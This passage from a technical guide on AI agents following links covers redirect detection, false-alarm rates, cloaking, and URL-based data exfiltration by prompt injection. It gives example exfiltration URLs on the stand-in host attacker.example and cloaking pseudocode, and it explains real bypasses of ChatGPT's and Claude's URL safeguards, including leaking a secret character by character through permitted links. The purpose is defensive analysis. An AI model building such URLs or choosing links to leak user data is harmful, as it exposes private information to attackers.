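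SpiderWeb detected 83% of the malicious graphs with a false-positive rate of 1.2%. The test covered only 196 graphs, 25 of them malicious. Without the features that described the graph as a whole, detection fell to 33%.

The two studies disagree about long chains. In *Shady Paths*, a long chain was a mild sign that a page was harmless, and a short one was a mild sign that it was malicious. The difference may come from the data, since advertising networks and login systems produce many long, legitimate chains that would be less common in tweets. Çolhak and colleagues (2026) counted more redirects on harmless sites than on phishing sites, which is another reason not to rely on length alone.

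SpiderWeb needed at least four distinct chains to the same destination before it could judge a page, and worked best with six or more. In a simulation with 10,914 visits to malicious pages, it would have blocked 93% of them but left the first visitors to each page unprotected. A single agent usually has only one chain, so the method is more useful to a browser maker, a security company or a large AI provider that can combine many users' chains, though this requires collecting records of where those users go.

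More recent work uses shared infrastructure to find related links. *PhishLumos* (2025) describes a system of AI agents that investigates phishing campaigns when the pages are inaccessible. In those cases, two detectors that compare screenshots scored 0.023 and 0.000 on a scale where 1 is perfect. PhishLumos instead looked for patterns in the addresses. In one campaign, it used an unusual string in the path of the first URL to find 540 more malicious links.

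In another campaign, PhishLumos searched for chains that began on a suspicious domain and ended on a particular official site, and found 281 new links. An agent's developer should be careful about treating a mismatch between the first and last domains as a sign of malice, because newsletters' tracking links often show it too. The search worked because it also specified the pair of domains and a range of dates.

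An expander can also request the same link twice, from different networks or with different browser settings, and compare the results. A difference is worth investigating, but advertising networks and sites with regional versions also send different visitors to different pages. For a single agent, the chain is mainly useful as a source of addresses to check against known ones.

### Why most alarms are false

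Even a good detector produces mostly false alarms if malicious links are rare. Suppose an agent checks 100,000 links, 100 of them malicious, using a detector that catches 95% of the malicious links and wrongly flags 1% of the harmless ones. It would flag 95 malicious links and 999 harmless ones, so about 91% of its alarms would be false.

| | Malicious | Harmless | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flagged | 95 | 999 | 1,094 |
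| Not flagged | 5 | 98,901 | 98,906 |
| Total | 100 | 99,900 | 100,000 |

Only 95 of the 1,094 flagged links (8.7%) are malicious. The detector is still useful, because a flagged link is 87 times as likely to be malicious as an average one.

*Benchmarking Large Language Models for Zero-shot and Few-shot Phishing URL Detection* (Hasan and BusiReddyGari, 2026) tested how well three older models classify URLs from the text alone. On a test set that was half phishing, Claude 3.7 Sonnet classified about 88% of URLs correctly, and about 88% of the URLs it flagged were phishing. Its accuracy was also 88% on a sample of 1,000 URLs with only ten phishing links. However, the published figures imply that it caught nine of the ten and flagged 118 harmless URLs, so only about 7% of the URLs it flagged were phishing. Grok 3 Beta did best of the three at that ratio, with 28%.

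Lowering the false-alarm rate helps more than catching the last few malicious links. At a rate of 0.1%, the example above would have about 100 false alarms, and almost half of all alarms would be correct. Small tests cannot establish a rate that low. Two models in ScamWorld raised no false alarms on the 53 legitimate sites, but a model with a true rate of 5% could do the same by chance.

A second check can also remove most of the false alarms. Sending the 1,094 flagged links to another detector with the same error rates would leave about 90 malicious and 10 harmless links. This works only if the two detectors make different mistakes. Two models that read the same URL would probably be misled by many of the same disguises, so the second check should use other evidence, such as the page itself.

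ReDence shows that a thorough investigation can keep false alarms very low. It explores a site, fills in forms with invented details and searches for outside evidence. In the October test, it examined 552,809 sites and flagged 4,054, of which 12 were not confirmed as scams. A check of 2,000 sites it had cleared found one scam, which suggests that it missed a few hundred in all. An investigation took a median of 44 seconds in earlier tests, which is too slow for every link but acceptable for the few that a faster check has flagged.

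### Blocking, warning and asking

A match on a good reputation list usually justifies blocking the link automatically, because somebody has identified that specific address as a threat. A host that imitates a known supplier's domain is also a good reason to block, if the software can compare it with the real domain.

When the evidence is weaker, whether to block a link depends on how much harm each kind of mistake would do. In the example, blocking every flagged link would stop 95 malicious visits and 999 harmless ones, or about 10.5 harmless visits for each malicious one. Blocking is therefore worthwhile if a malicious visit would do more than about 10.5 times as much harm as wrongly refusing a link. That is probably true for an agent signed in to someone's email, but it may not be for one that reads public pages on an isolated machine with no private data.

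The software can also respond to a weak warning by limiting what the agent can do. It could open the page in a browser without the user's logins, or let the agent read the page but not type into it. A false alarm then causes little disruption, since the agent can still read most harmless pages.

If the agent asked about every alarm, Ruth would see about eleven or twelve questions for each malicious link, and would probably learn to approve them without reading. The agent should ask only before actions with serious consequences, such as entering a password or making a payment, and should give her a fact she can check. "This invoice link leads to `attacker.example`, but your supplier uses `example.com`" gives her a much clearer reason to refuse than "This link may be unsafe."

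## How the request itself can leak data

A link expander can follow a shortened URL without showing the agent the page, but its first request still sends a complete URL to someone else's server. If that URL contains private data, blocking the link afterward doesn't prevent the leak.

Suppose a hidden instruction in an email causes the model to open `https://attacker.example/collect?data=overdue-loan`, where `overdue-loan` describes something in Ruth's inbox. The attacker's server logs the address and redirects the client to the genuine invoice at `docs.example.com`. The expander reports a harmless destination, but the attacker already has the information, whether or not the agent opens the invoice.

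Developers can easily overlook that a tool that only reads can still send data out in its requests. PolicyLayer's catalogue rates one such tool, the link expander *onyx_url_unshorten*, which agents can call, as "Low Risk" and read-only. Anthropic warns developers that website publishers may keep any parameters in a URL that Anthropic's own fetch tool requests.

### What each server in a chain learns

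The attacker could also send the data through the open redirect on the supplier's site:

`https://docs.example.com/go?to=https%3A%2F%2Fattacker.example%2Fcollect%3Fdata%3Doverdue-loan`

| Server | What it receives | What its operator learns |
|---|---|---|
| DNS servers | The host names `docs.example.com` and `attacker.example` | Which hosts the client is about to contact |
| `docs.example.com` | The whole link, including the encoded URL | The words "overdue-loan" and the next address |
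| `attacker.example` | `/collect?data=overdue-loan` | The words "overdue-loan" |
| Any later server | The URL that the attacker's server puts in its Location header | Whatever the attacker passes on |

Each web server also learns the time, the client's network address and usually the name of its software.

Checking every hop would help with this link, because the tool would refuse `attacker.example` after the first response and the words would reach only the supplier's logs. The direct link goes straight to the attacker's server, so the tool has to check the URL before it sends anything, including a DNS lookup. If the model opens `https://overdue-loan.attacker.example/`, the attacker's DNS server receives the words before the client connects.

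Redirecting servers cannot see the agent's conversation. They can pass on data from the request, but they can't add an email subject line that the request did not contain. To prevent this kind of leak, the tool mainly needs to check the URL the model supplies and any credentials the tool itself attaches. It still has to check every later URL for the other two harms, malicious pages and private addresses.

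### Why a list of trusted hosts is not enough

OpenAI points out that restricting an agent to links on well-known sites fails if the software checks only the first host, because a permitted site can redirect the agent to one that isn't permitted. Oasis Security's *Claudy Day* describes an open redirect on Anthropic's site, at `claude.com/redirect/`. Google's advertising system checked only the host name, so an attacker could buy a search ad that displayed a `claude.com` address and led to a prompt injection.

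Checking each hop fixes that problem, but some trusted hosts let outsiders collect data directly. The software developer Simon Willison keeps dated notes on such cases, all of which security researchers demonstrated:

| Product | Host on its list | How data could get out |
|---|---|---|
| Superhuman AI, an email assistant | `docs.google.com` | A Google Form saved data from the requested URL |
| Claude Cowork | `api.anthropic.com` | The agent uploaded files using the attacker's own Anthropic key |
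| Google Antigravity, a programming tool | `webhook.site` | Anyone can create an address there and read the requests it receives |
| Salesforce Agentforce | Subdomains of `my-salesforce-cms.com` | The domain had expired, so the researchers registered it themselves |

None of these attacks needed a redirect. An allowlist protects private data only if outsiders cannot read what reaches the listed hosts, and Willison calls finding such hosts a "tricky proposition". OpenAI says strict lists also cause frequent false alarms.

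### ChatGPT's URL filter

OpenAI's present approach came after almost three years of reports about leaks from ChatGPT. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* recounts this history from the perspective of Johann Rehberger, the security researcher who reported the problem in early 2023. An attacker could get the model to include an image in its answer, with private text in the image's URL. ChatGPT requested the image to display it, which sent out the private text without the user clicking anything. Rehberger reported the same flaw in Bing Chat, and Microsoft restricted image loading there in May 2023.

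OpenAI added a filter called `url_safe` in December 2023. When a link or image appeared in a chat, ChatGPT sent its URL to OpenAI's servers, which classified it as safe or unsafe. OpenAI did not explain how the classification worked. Rehberger found ways around the filter and found that the macOS and iOS apps didn't use it.

Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* describes how a redirect link got past ChatGPT's URL filter. The filter accepted every URL on `bing.com`, including the links in Bing's search results, which redirect to the listed sites. Researchers at Tenable, a security company, got their own site into Bing's index and copied its link. The filter approved the link, and ChatGPT loaded an image from the researchers' site. Tenable reported the flaw on December 10, 2024, and asked for updates until March 2025. The flaw was still open when Tenable published.

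A Bing link of this kind leads to one fixed page, so an attacker probably could not add arbitrary text to it. But the attacker could prepare several links and have the model choose between them. According to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, a January 2026 news report, the security company Radware used this idea against a later version of ChatGPT's protection. Its attack, ZombieAgent, supplied ready-made URLs that each ended in a different letter or digit. OpenAI then stopped ChatGPT from opening links in emails unless they met certain conditions, such as appearing in a well-known public index.

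On January 28, 2026, OpenAI published the rule behind its newer protection. It concerns the exact URL instead of the host's reputation:

1. A crawler records public URLs, as a search engine does, with no access to users' conversations or accounts.
2. Before an agent fetches a URL automatically, OpenAI's software looks for that URL in the crawler's index.
3. If the URL is there, the agent can load it.
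4. If not, the software tells the agent to try another site or asks the user first.

A URL that already existed on the public web, independently of the user's conversation, is unlikely to contain that user's secrets. In the warning dialog, titled "Check this link is safe", the user sees the URL and a notice that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation with another site. The user can then copy or open the link.

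OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) calls this protection Safe Url. The protection also covers page visits in Atlas, OpenAI's browser, and in Deep Research, its tool for long research tasks. OpenAI says the model refuses to send the data in most of the attacks it knows of. The URL rule is meant for cases where the model is fooled. OpenAI reproduces one such attack, a 2025 email disguised as a note about restructuring, which worked in half of its tests.

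### A public short link and a new one

OpenAI's announcement doesn't describe what its software does when an indexed URL redirects to one outside the index. This probably matters little for leaks, since the redirecting server has received only a public URL. It matters more for malicious pages, and OpenAI states that the rule doesn't guarantee a page is trustworthy.

Suppose Ruth's supplier printed `https://short.example/catalog` in a press release two years ago. A crawler has probably recorded it, so the agent can open it without asking. The link contains nothing about Ruth. But its owner may have changed the destination since then, so the agent still needs to run the other checks on the chain.

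The supplier created `https://short.example/q7Xk` this morning for one email. No crawler has visited it, so the agent has to ask Ruth or look for the invoice elsewhere. If the email is genuine, the agent has raised a false alarm. Many links in private email have the same problem, including password resets and tracking links made for one recipient.

The software cannot tell from the URL alone whether a short link is harmless or leaks data. An attacker who runs a link-shortening service can log every code that clients request, even codes that lead nowhere. The attacker could tell the model to use the last four digits of a user's bank card as the code, and the resulting URL, `https://short.example/4471`, would look like an ordinary short link. To tell the two apart, the software has to know whether the URL came from an email or the model composed it.

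### Anthropic's conversation rule

Anthropic's web fetch tool for developers opens a URL only if it has already appeared in the conversation. The tool accepts URLs from the user's messages, from the results of tools that the developer's application runs, and from earlier web searches and fetches. It refuses URLs that Claude generates, so the model cannot add private text to an address and open it. Anthropic later gave this refusal its own error code, `url_not_in_prior_context`.

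The two companies' rules give different results for ordinary links:

| Link | OpenAI's public-URL rule | Anthropic's conversation rule |
|---|---|---|
| An old public short link in a search result | Opens it if the crawler has recorded it | Permits it |
| `q7Xk`, in an email that the developer's tool returned | Asks Ruth, or tells the agent to try elsewhere | Permits it |
| `q7Xk`, typed into the chat by Ruth | Opens it, as Rehberger understands the rule | Permits it |
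| A public page whose address the model remembers from training | Opens it if the crawler has recorded it | Refuses it until the URL appears in the conversation |
| An address that the model builds from Ruth's emails | Asks Ruth, or tells the agent to try elsewhere | Refuses it |

Anthropic's rule suits an email agent better because it lets through new links that Ruth's correspondents have sent her, but it also lets through every link an attacker has sent. When the tool came out, Willison (2025) objected that a "user message" often contains text from strangers. A developer might paste a customer's email into the message and ask for a summary, and the tool would treat any URL in the email as one the user had supplied.

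Willison still considered the ban on URLs that Claude makes up the most valuable part of the rule, because most attacks of this kind depend on building an address that contains the stolen data. Anthropic doesn't claim complete protection either, and advises developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. Developers concerned about leaks can limit the number of fetches, restrict the tool to known hosts, or turn it off. The tool also rejects URLs longer than 250 characters, which limits how much data one address can hold but may also block some long tracking links.

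### Leaking data by choosing between permitted links

Both rules prevent the model from writing new data into a URL. Neither can prevent it from choosing between several permitted URLs, and the choice itself is information. If a site has 36 pages, one for each letter and digit, a request for one of them tells the site's owner which character the model picked. Three requests in order allow

36 × 36 × 36 = 46,656

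different messages, more than enough to identify any four-digit PIN. The attacker still has to persuade the model to play along.

Rehberger described this method in 2023. According to Embrace The Red, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, OpenAI's technical paper on the rule, acknowledges that the method still works. The attacker's pages must be in the crawler's index, but many larger websites already have 36 indexed pages. A site with thousands of indexed pages could assign a page to each word.

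In *The Memory Heist*, Paul (2026) found the same weakness in the consumer version of Claude. Its fetch tool accepted URLs typed by the user, returned by a web search, or linked from a page it had already fetched. Paul built a site on which each page linked to further pages, one for each possible next letter. Claude never composed a URL, but the links it followed spelled out the information Paul wanted. He disguised the task as a login step for AI assistants and obtained his own name, employer and home town, which Claude knew from earlier conversations.

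Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally. Willison (2026) reports that the company closed the hole by stopping the consumer tool from following links on pages it had fetched. This is effective but restricts the tool heavily, because following links is a large part of browsing. According to its documentation, the developer version could still follow such links in August 2026, so the fix may not cover agents that developers build themselves.

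Rehberger suggests that the software either keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it, or refuse to request the same URL twice in a session. Either remedy would stop an attacker from using one page repeatedly for the same letter. But this does little to protect a short secret, because three requests without repetition still allow 36 × 35 × 34 = 42,840 messages. An attacker can also prepare several pages for each letter. Rehberger expects limited leaks to continue.

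A limit on the total number of requests is easier to reason about. Anthropic's tool has one, called `max_uses`, which has no default value. If a developer sets it to five, requests to a set of 36 pages can still encode any of about 60 million five-character messages. That is enough for a PIN or a date of birth, but not the contents of an email. The limit therefore protects documents much better than short secrets, and a developer whose agent handles short secrets should keep them out of the model's reach while it browses.

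### How often a small model leaked data

In *Silent Egress*, Lan and colleagues measured these leaks by monitoring network traffic instead of reading the model's answers. The agent had to summarize a page containing an instruction to send a fake access key to a collecting server. The researchers varied where on the page the instruction appeared, whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether the key was to be sent whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

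Data reached the server in 423 runs, or 88%, which the paper's abstract gives as about 0.89. In 120 control runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted that server. Redirects of up to three hops barely changed the rate, which was 0.88 for direct links and 0.89 for redirected ones. This is expected, since the instruction is on the final page and the model reads the same text either way.

In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's answer gave no sign of the leak. A filter that checks only the answer would have missed these attacks, so a developer needs a record of the agent's requests.

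Splitting the key made the attack less reliable but harder to spot. On average across the paper's results, the attack worked in about 99% of runs when the agent sent the whole key and 77% when it sent pieces. Lan and colleagues report that sensitive data appeared in the first request in 26% of the split runs and in the first three requests in 16%. By their own definition, the second figure can't be smaller than the first, so at least one of them must be wrong.

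They then tested defenses, using only direct links and whole keys:

| Defense | Model tried to send the key | Data got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| A warning in the system prompt to ignore instructions in web content | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags that mark web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Both of these | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| An allowlist of four hosts | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
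| A filter for words such as `api_key` and `password` | 23.3% | 0% |
| A filter for random-looking text | 0% | 0% |

The allowlist result is convincing, though unsurprising. The model tried to send the key every time, and ordinary code blocked it every time because the attacker's host wasn't on the list. Warnings and tags depended on the model acting on them, which this small model often failed to do. The larger models now in use would probably do better with them.

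The name "redirect detection" is misleading because the defense followed no redirects and the test contained none. The defense blocked numeric addresses, eight top-level domains such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as `steal` or `collect`. The sample attack in the paper uses the path `/collect`, so the attacker could probably have gotten past the defense by renaming it. The paper's abstract lists redirect-chain analysis among its more effective controls, but this experiment provides no evidence about it.

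The results for the two text filters are also hard to interpret. A filter that examines a finished request should not affect how often the model tries to make one, yet the attempt rate fell to 23.3% with one filter and to zero with the other. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking text while the filter was on, but it is unclear how the model would have known it was on.

To defend against more capable attackers, they propose tracking where data comes from, though they did not build or test this. The software would label everything from a web page as untrusted and apply the same label to any request the page influenced. It could then block the request or ask the user, even if the URL contained only a harmless-looking fragment of a key.

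### Automatic link previews

A leak does not require the agent to open anything. Many people talk to agents through messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram, which show a title and picture for each link in a message. To get them, the app requests the page. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* explains how an attacker can use this:

1. A hidden instruction makes the model put private data into a URL on the attacker's host.
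2. The agent includes the link in its reply to the user.
3. The messaging app requests the URL to build a preview.
4. The attacker reads the data in the server's log.

When a chat app fetches a link preview, the user doesn't have to click and the agent's page-opening tool makes no request, so the tool's host lists and hop checks never run. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, an open-source agent, was exposed by default when used through Telegram. Its owner can prevent this by setting `linkPreview` to `false` in the Telegram section of its configuration file. According to Willison (2024), Rehberger pointed out that an application can turn off Slack previews for each message it posts by setting `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to `false`.

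Email can leak data in a similar way. In May 2026, Willison described an attack on Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, which could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval. These messages could contain images from outside sites, and opening a message sent requests for those images. The image URLs could include download links that gave the attacker access to the user's files.

Developers should apply their URL rule to every URL the agent writes, as well as those it opens. If a link in a reply fails the rule, the software can remove it or show it as plain text with previews turned off.

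Rehberger still worries that some OpenAI developers may not know about the company's rule and may leave it out of a new feature. A flaw in ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode shows how a protection can miss a feature. The mode restricts features that malicious instructions could use to send data out of a conversation, but *ChatGPT Locked the Doors and Left a Window Open* (Brinsa, 2026) recounts how the security company Check Point found a way around it. According to Capstone Technologies Group's *ChatGPT Lockdown Mode Bypass Exfiltrates Chats Without User Interaction*, the gap was in the desktop app's previews of HTML pages, and OpenAI fixed it on September 18, 2026.

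## Why the chain that was checked may not be the chain that is followed

Software can inspect a URL for private data before sending it, but it cannot inspect the redirects in the same way, because other people's servers send them and may respond differently to a check than to the agent. If an expander follows Ruth's link to a genuine invoice, its developer knows only where the link led for that expander, at that moment, without a click.

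When software checks a link with a separate request before the agent's visit, the agent may follow a different chain. Programmers use the term "time of check to time of use" for the general fault in which a program checks something, then acts as though nothing has changed since. *Mind the Gap* (2025) applies the term to language-model agents, which have a gap between any two actions.

In the classic version of this problem, a program checks that it may open a file, but an attacker puts a different file under the same name before the program opens it. *Atomicity for Agents* (Jiang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) explains that a file name is not a stable reference to a particular file. A URL is even less stable, because a server can send two visitors to different places at the same instant.

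### Different visitors, different redirects

Cloaking means serving different content or redirects to different visitors. Suppose the attacker runs `click.example`, the second host in Ruth's chain, with these rules:

```
if the visitor's address belongs to a cloud provider or VPN:
    redirect to https://docs.example.com/invoices/1042
otherwise:
    redirect to https://docs.example.com.attacker.example/login
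```

An expander in a cloud data center would reach the genuine invoice, while Ruth's agent, which works from her office computer, would reach the fake login page.

Infoblox's *Parked Domains Become Weapons with Direct Search Advertising* (2025) documents a real case that works almost the same way. The domain was a misspelling of a bank's, and its owner made money by selling the visits to advertisers. Visitors from cloud services and commercial VPNs got a page of advertising links, while visitors from home connections got a 302 redirect into a series of advertising systems. In more than 1,000 visits through home connections and the Tor anonymity network, the researchers never saw the page of links, and about 90% of the visits ended at scams, malware or unwanted content.

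An expander that passes the first test may fail a later one. An Infoblox researcher told Krebs on Security (2025) that the systems profiled the device again at each handoff and sent unwanted visitors to a decoy such as Amazon's site.

Attackers can buy software that does this. In 2016, Invernizzi, Thomas and colleagues, in *Cloak of Visibility*, examined ten cloaking programs from underground forums, priced from $167 to $13,188. They listed the signals that the six most sophisticated ones used:

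| Signal | Programs that used it |
|---|---|
| Network address | 6 |
| Browser name in the User-Agent header | 6 |
| Referring page, where the visitor found the link | 6 |
| Host name registered for the network address | 4 |
| Country | 4 |
| Whether the client runs JavaScript | 3 |
| Search keywords | 2 |
| Time window | 2 |
| Order of the visitor's actions | 2 |

One list of addresses to avoid covered 51.7 million, including those of 30 security companies and several cloud providers.

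The researchers then requested 135,577 URLs from Google's search results and advertisements while posing as 11 kinds of visitor. They found cloaking against Google's crawler in 11.7% of the search results and 4.9% of the advertisements. These ten-year-old figures don't represent the whole web, because the researchers had searched for terms that scammers favor, such as luxury goods and weight-loss supplements.

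More recently, *An Analysis of Architectural and Operational Dynamics of Phishkits in the Wild* found some form of evasion in about 78% of 1,300 phishing kits from 2020 to 2023. Another study, cited in *PhishParrot* (Nakano, Koide and Chiba, 2025), found cloaking in 96.5% of 2,933 kits. Much of the evasion is crude. In the first collection, 126 kits used nearly the same list of blocked addresses, and one kit blocked any visitor whose internet provider had "University" in its name.

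Other attackers select their visitors more carefully. Keitaro is a commercial program that advertisers use to send visitors to different pages based on their country, device, browser or referring page. In a study with the advertising security company Confiant, Infoblox describes a gambling operation that used Keitaro between October 2025 and January 2026. The operation almost exclusively targeted Android users in Germany and Windows users in the United States or Switzerland. Visitors it didn't target saw a mobile game company's decoy site or a Google page such as YouTube.

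The usual remedy is to make the checker look like the intended victim. PhishParrot first visits a suspicious URL normally and looks for similar cases in its records. A language model then suggests browser settings, a country and a type of network for a second visit. Over 21 days and 32,487 URLs, this method improved phishing detection by up to 33.8% over a standard scanner. It used 91 different visitor profiles, so a single profile would not have been enough. Each URL took an average of 16.7 seconds.

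An agent's developer has an easier task, because the expander only has to imitate the agent. It can use the same browser, language settings and network. But matching the agent this closely conflicts with the reasons for isolating an expander. On Ruth's office network, the expander could reach private machines, and with her cookies, it would act as Ruth. If it doesn't use her cookies, the server can still tell its visit from the agent's.

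### Pages served only to AI agents

Cloaking can also work the other way, showing people a harmless page and agents a harmful one. Zychlinski (2025), in *A Whole New World*, calls the result a "parallel-poisoned web". In the paper's test, a website served ordinary software documentation to people. When it detected an agent, it served a page with instructions to authenticate using a secret key stored on the user's computer, including the command for reading the key.

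The attack succeeded with Claude 4 Sonnet, GPT-5 Fast and Gemini 2.5 Pro. The test covered only one internal website, one programming agent (Cursor) and these three models, which are now old, with no count of attempts. It shows that the attack can work, but not how often it would.

In October 2026, Chen, Chen and Karray (*Agent-Targeted Cloaking on the Web*, 2026) looked for real sites that serve different content to AI agents. They requested the same pages repeatedly, changing only the User-Agent header, and repeated the request as Chrome to measure how much each page varied on its own. The main sample contained 4,705 sites from a list of the 10,000 most popular domains.

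| Name in the request | Sites that refused it | Sites that served a different page |
|---|---|---|
| Chrome, repeated | 0.2% | 0.9% |
| Firefox | 0.5% | 1.3% |
| An unknown research bot | 5.7% | 2.9% |
| Claude-User | 17.7% | 3.2% |
| ChatGPT-User | 21.2% | 4.6% |

Most of the differences were refusals, and most of the altered pages had ordinary explanations, such as a simplified version for any visitor that isn't a browser. Only four sites addressed AI systems in text that browsers did not receive. Three served notes or documentation for AI readers. The fourth, a major news publisher, gave AI agents a bank's sponsored text that neither browsers nor Google's crawler received.

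Malicious pages that target agents therefore seem rare on popular sites. That is reassuring if an agent mostly reads well-known sites, but it is weak evidence about links in phishing emails, which often lead to domains that an attacker registered a few days earlier.

Because of these refusals, an expander that identifies itself as Chrome may see a page that the agent never gets. Copying the agent's name does not solve this if a vendor runs the fetcher. Chen and colleagues used Anthropic's real fetcher to request 180 pages that had refused their imitation of it, and it received 77% of them. The real fetcher sends requests from addresses that Anthropic has published, which a developer's own expander cannot use.

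Chen and colleagues suggest fetching each page as a browser too, and flagging any text that appears only in the agent's copy. The comparison has to allow for pages that change constantly, because otherwise it would have flagged 7.2% of sites by chance.

### Destinations that change after the check

An attacker doesn't need to recognize the scanner if the scanner always comes first. The security company Kaspersky describes "delayed phishing", in which an emailed link leads to nothing, or to a harmless page, until the message has passed the mail filter. With an editable short link and invented times, the attack on Ruth could go like this:

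| Time | Event |
|---|---|
| 09:00 | The attacker points `q7Xk` at a harmless page and emails Ruth |
| 09:01 | The company's mail filter expands the link, finds the harmless page and stores that result |
| 09:12 | The attacker changes the destination to the fake login page |
| 09:14 | Ruth asks for a summary, and the agent's software approves the link from the stored result |
| 09:15 | The agent opens the link and reaches the fake login page |

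The result was 14 minutes old when the agent relied on it, but other results may be years old. Check Point Research's *From Trust to Threat* (2025) reported that attackers had taken over expired invitation links to servers on the chat service Discord by registering the old codes for their own servers. Links that people had posted on trusted sites then began leading to malware.

A change of domain owner has the same effect. Infoblox warns that AI chat systems may give outdated URLs from their training data, and that criminals can buy those domains once they expire. An agent that uses a URL from its training data is relying on a check that nobody has repeated since training.

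Email security companies respond by checking links again when someone clicks them. Microsoft's Safe Links scans URLs while a message is in transit and verifies them when the reader clicks. KnowBe4's *Defend Link Scanning Overview* describes the same arrangement and explains that attackers may leave a site inactive until the first scan is over. In the timeline, expanding the link again at 09:14 would have revealed the fake login page.

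A recent check is much better than an old one, but the attacker can defeat it by counting requests, without having to time the switch. The server can return the harmless redirect to the first request for `q7Xk` and the malicious one to the second. If only Ruth received that code, the first request probably comes from a scanner.

Attackers can also change a chain after a target has followed it. Gen Digital's *The phishing link that died on purpose* describes Mailer-Go, a bulk phishing platform that makes a separate tracking link for each recipient. The operator replaced domains once defenders identified them, and much of the chain was built to disappear after a useful click. Developers should therefore log every hop during the agent's visit, since an investigator who follows the link the next day may find nothing.

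### Redirects that wait for the visitor to act

A page can delay its redirect until the visitor clicks a button, solves a CAPTCHA or waits. An expander that reads only headers and refresh tags finds no redirect and reports that page as the final destination.

According to Push Security's *Delayed execution*, phishing sites use delays and series of redirects to outlast scanners, which examine each page for a limited time. Phishing sites also use common services for keeping out bots, some of which can test visitors without showing them anything. *Broken Gates* (2026) describes two of these services. Google's reCAPTCHA v3 scores each visit from 0 to 1 based on the visitor's behavior and browser, without a puzzle. Cloudflare's Turnstile checks the browser in the background, with or without a visible checkbox.

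*TraceScope* (Zhang, Reber and colleagues, 2026) gives an idea of how many phishing sites scanners miss this way. Of the 111 URLs submitted to its system in real use, 40 were offline. Another 18 worked normally for people but appeared unavailable to a standard automated browser, often with a "403 Forbidden" error, so a simple scanner would have counted them as dead too.

The researchers' remedy is to have an AI agent play the victim in an isolated browser. The agent receives the text of the email and an invented identity, then clicks, types and solves simple puzzles such as "8+7". A second agent judges the recording. In a test on 708 URLs, 241 of them phishing, the system caught 78% of the phishing pages, and 94% of the pages it flagged were phishing. The researchers intend it for links that somebody has already reported or that a faster check has found doubtful.

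These pages are a particular danger to agents because a browser agent that can add 8 and 7, as in the example, may reach a page that the expander never reached. The software should treat a page that requires a click or a CAPTCHA as an unfinished chain, and check whatever URL the browser requests next.

### When the check changes something

GET is defined as "safe" in HTTP because the client is only asking to read something, but some sites make a change when they receive a GET request. For example, a login link may work only once, and opening a confirmation link may activate an account. If an expander requests such a link during the check, it uses up the login or activates the account before the agent follows the link.

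Email scanners have caused this problem for years. Auth0, a login provider, describes one case in *Brute-Force Unblock Link in Emails Consumed by Security Scanners*. When an account locks after too many wrong passwords, the owner is emailed a link to unlock it. If a security scanner requests the link first, that request unlocks the account, and the owner who then clicks the link sees an error saying that the URL can be used only once. The only workaround Auth0 offers is to make sure that no scanner opens the link.

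Users report similar trouble with login links. In *"Link protect" software breaks passwordless auth*, a post on Auth0's forum, a developer suspects that a customer's Mimecast email security software opened login links to generate previews, making the links useless to the customer. YU Yang (2019) started a discussion on Microsoft's forum, *O365 URL Scan/Safe Links impact to one-time URL*, that was still attracting complaints in 2023. These are individual reports, not measurements, but they describe the same fault in different products.

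A confirmation link can cause a more serious problem. Trusona, which sells login software, describes a hypothetical attack in which someone registers for a service with another person's email address. If the victim's email scanner opens the confirmation link, the service treats that as the owner's consent.

A scanner that visits an unsubscribe link can remove the subscriber by accident if the link needs only a GET request. Suped's *Why is Microsoft scanning links in my emails at a high rate* (2025), a guide for companies that send bulk email, includes advice on handling one-click unsubscribing safely when scanners visit. The IETF's standard for one-click unsubscribing requires a POST request, partly because mail software fetches links automatically.

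Site owners can prevent most of these accidents by showing a page with a button and making the change only after a POST request. Descope's *Checking for Email Scanners* describes a related method, in which the login service tries to detect the scanner and shows it an extra screen. Neither method is certain to stop a checker that behaves like a person, because an AI investigator that clicks "Continue" on a phishing site may also click "Confirm" on a genuine one.

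An agent's developer cannot control how other people's sites work. The software can skip advance checks on URLs containing words such as `verify`, `token` or `unsubscribe`, but a short link hides those words until the expander has followed it. Avoiding the extra request altogether is safer.

### Checking the agent's own request

An in-line check applies the rules for each hop to the agent's own request, so the chain it checks is the one the agent follows, and the last response is the page the agent reads.

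In Ruth's case, the tool on her computer would request the short link once. The request would look like it came from an ordinary office visitor, so the attacker's server would return the redirect to the fake login page. The tool would compare that page's host with the supplier's known domain and refuse to follow the redirect. The cloaking would not have helped the attacker, because the program checking the link was the same one the attacker wanted to send to the fake page.

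The two methods compare as follows:

| Cause of the difference | Advance check | In-line check |
|---|---|---|
| The server recognizes the scanner | May see a harmless chain | Sees the agent's own chain |
| Somebody changes the destination | Misses any change made after the check | Sees the current destination, but has to check again on the next visit |
| The redirect waits for a click or delay | Usually stops too early | Catches it if the tool checks every later request |
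| The link works only once | May use it up | Adds no extra request, but the agent's own visit still uses it up |
| The page changes after loading | Misses it | Misses it if the browser makes no new request |
| A permitted host serves a harmful page | Misses it unless the software also judges the page | Misses it unless the software also judges the page |

The in-line check must also control the address that the tool connects to, or DNS rebinding can reopen the gap.

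The tool determines how fully the gap between checking a page and using it can be closed. A simple fetcher can download a page, scan the text and give the model that same copy. A browser keeps running the page's code after the check, so the content can still change. Keitaro, for example, offers a script that replaces a page's content without changing its address, which a tool that watches only for redirects would not detect.

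Jiang and colleagues studied what happens when a page changes after an agent reads it but before the agent acts. On the Forbes homepage, an advertisement can appear where the agent is about to click, so the click opens the advertiser's site. They tested ten open-source browser agents and found the weakness was widespread. Their remedy records changes to the page while the model runs and cancels the action if any are relevant. This shortens the gap between check and click from several seconds to about a tenth of a second, but doesn't eliminate it, because a browser has no way to freeze a live page while the agent checks it and clicks.

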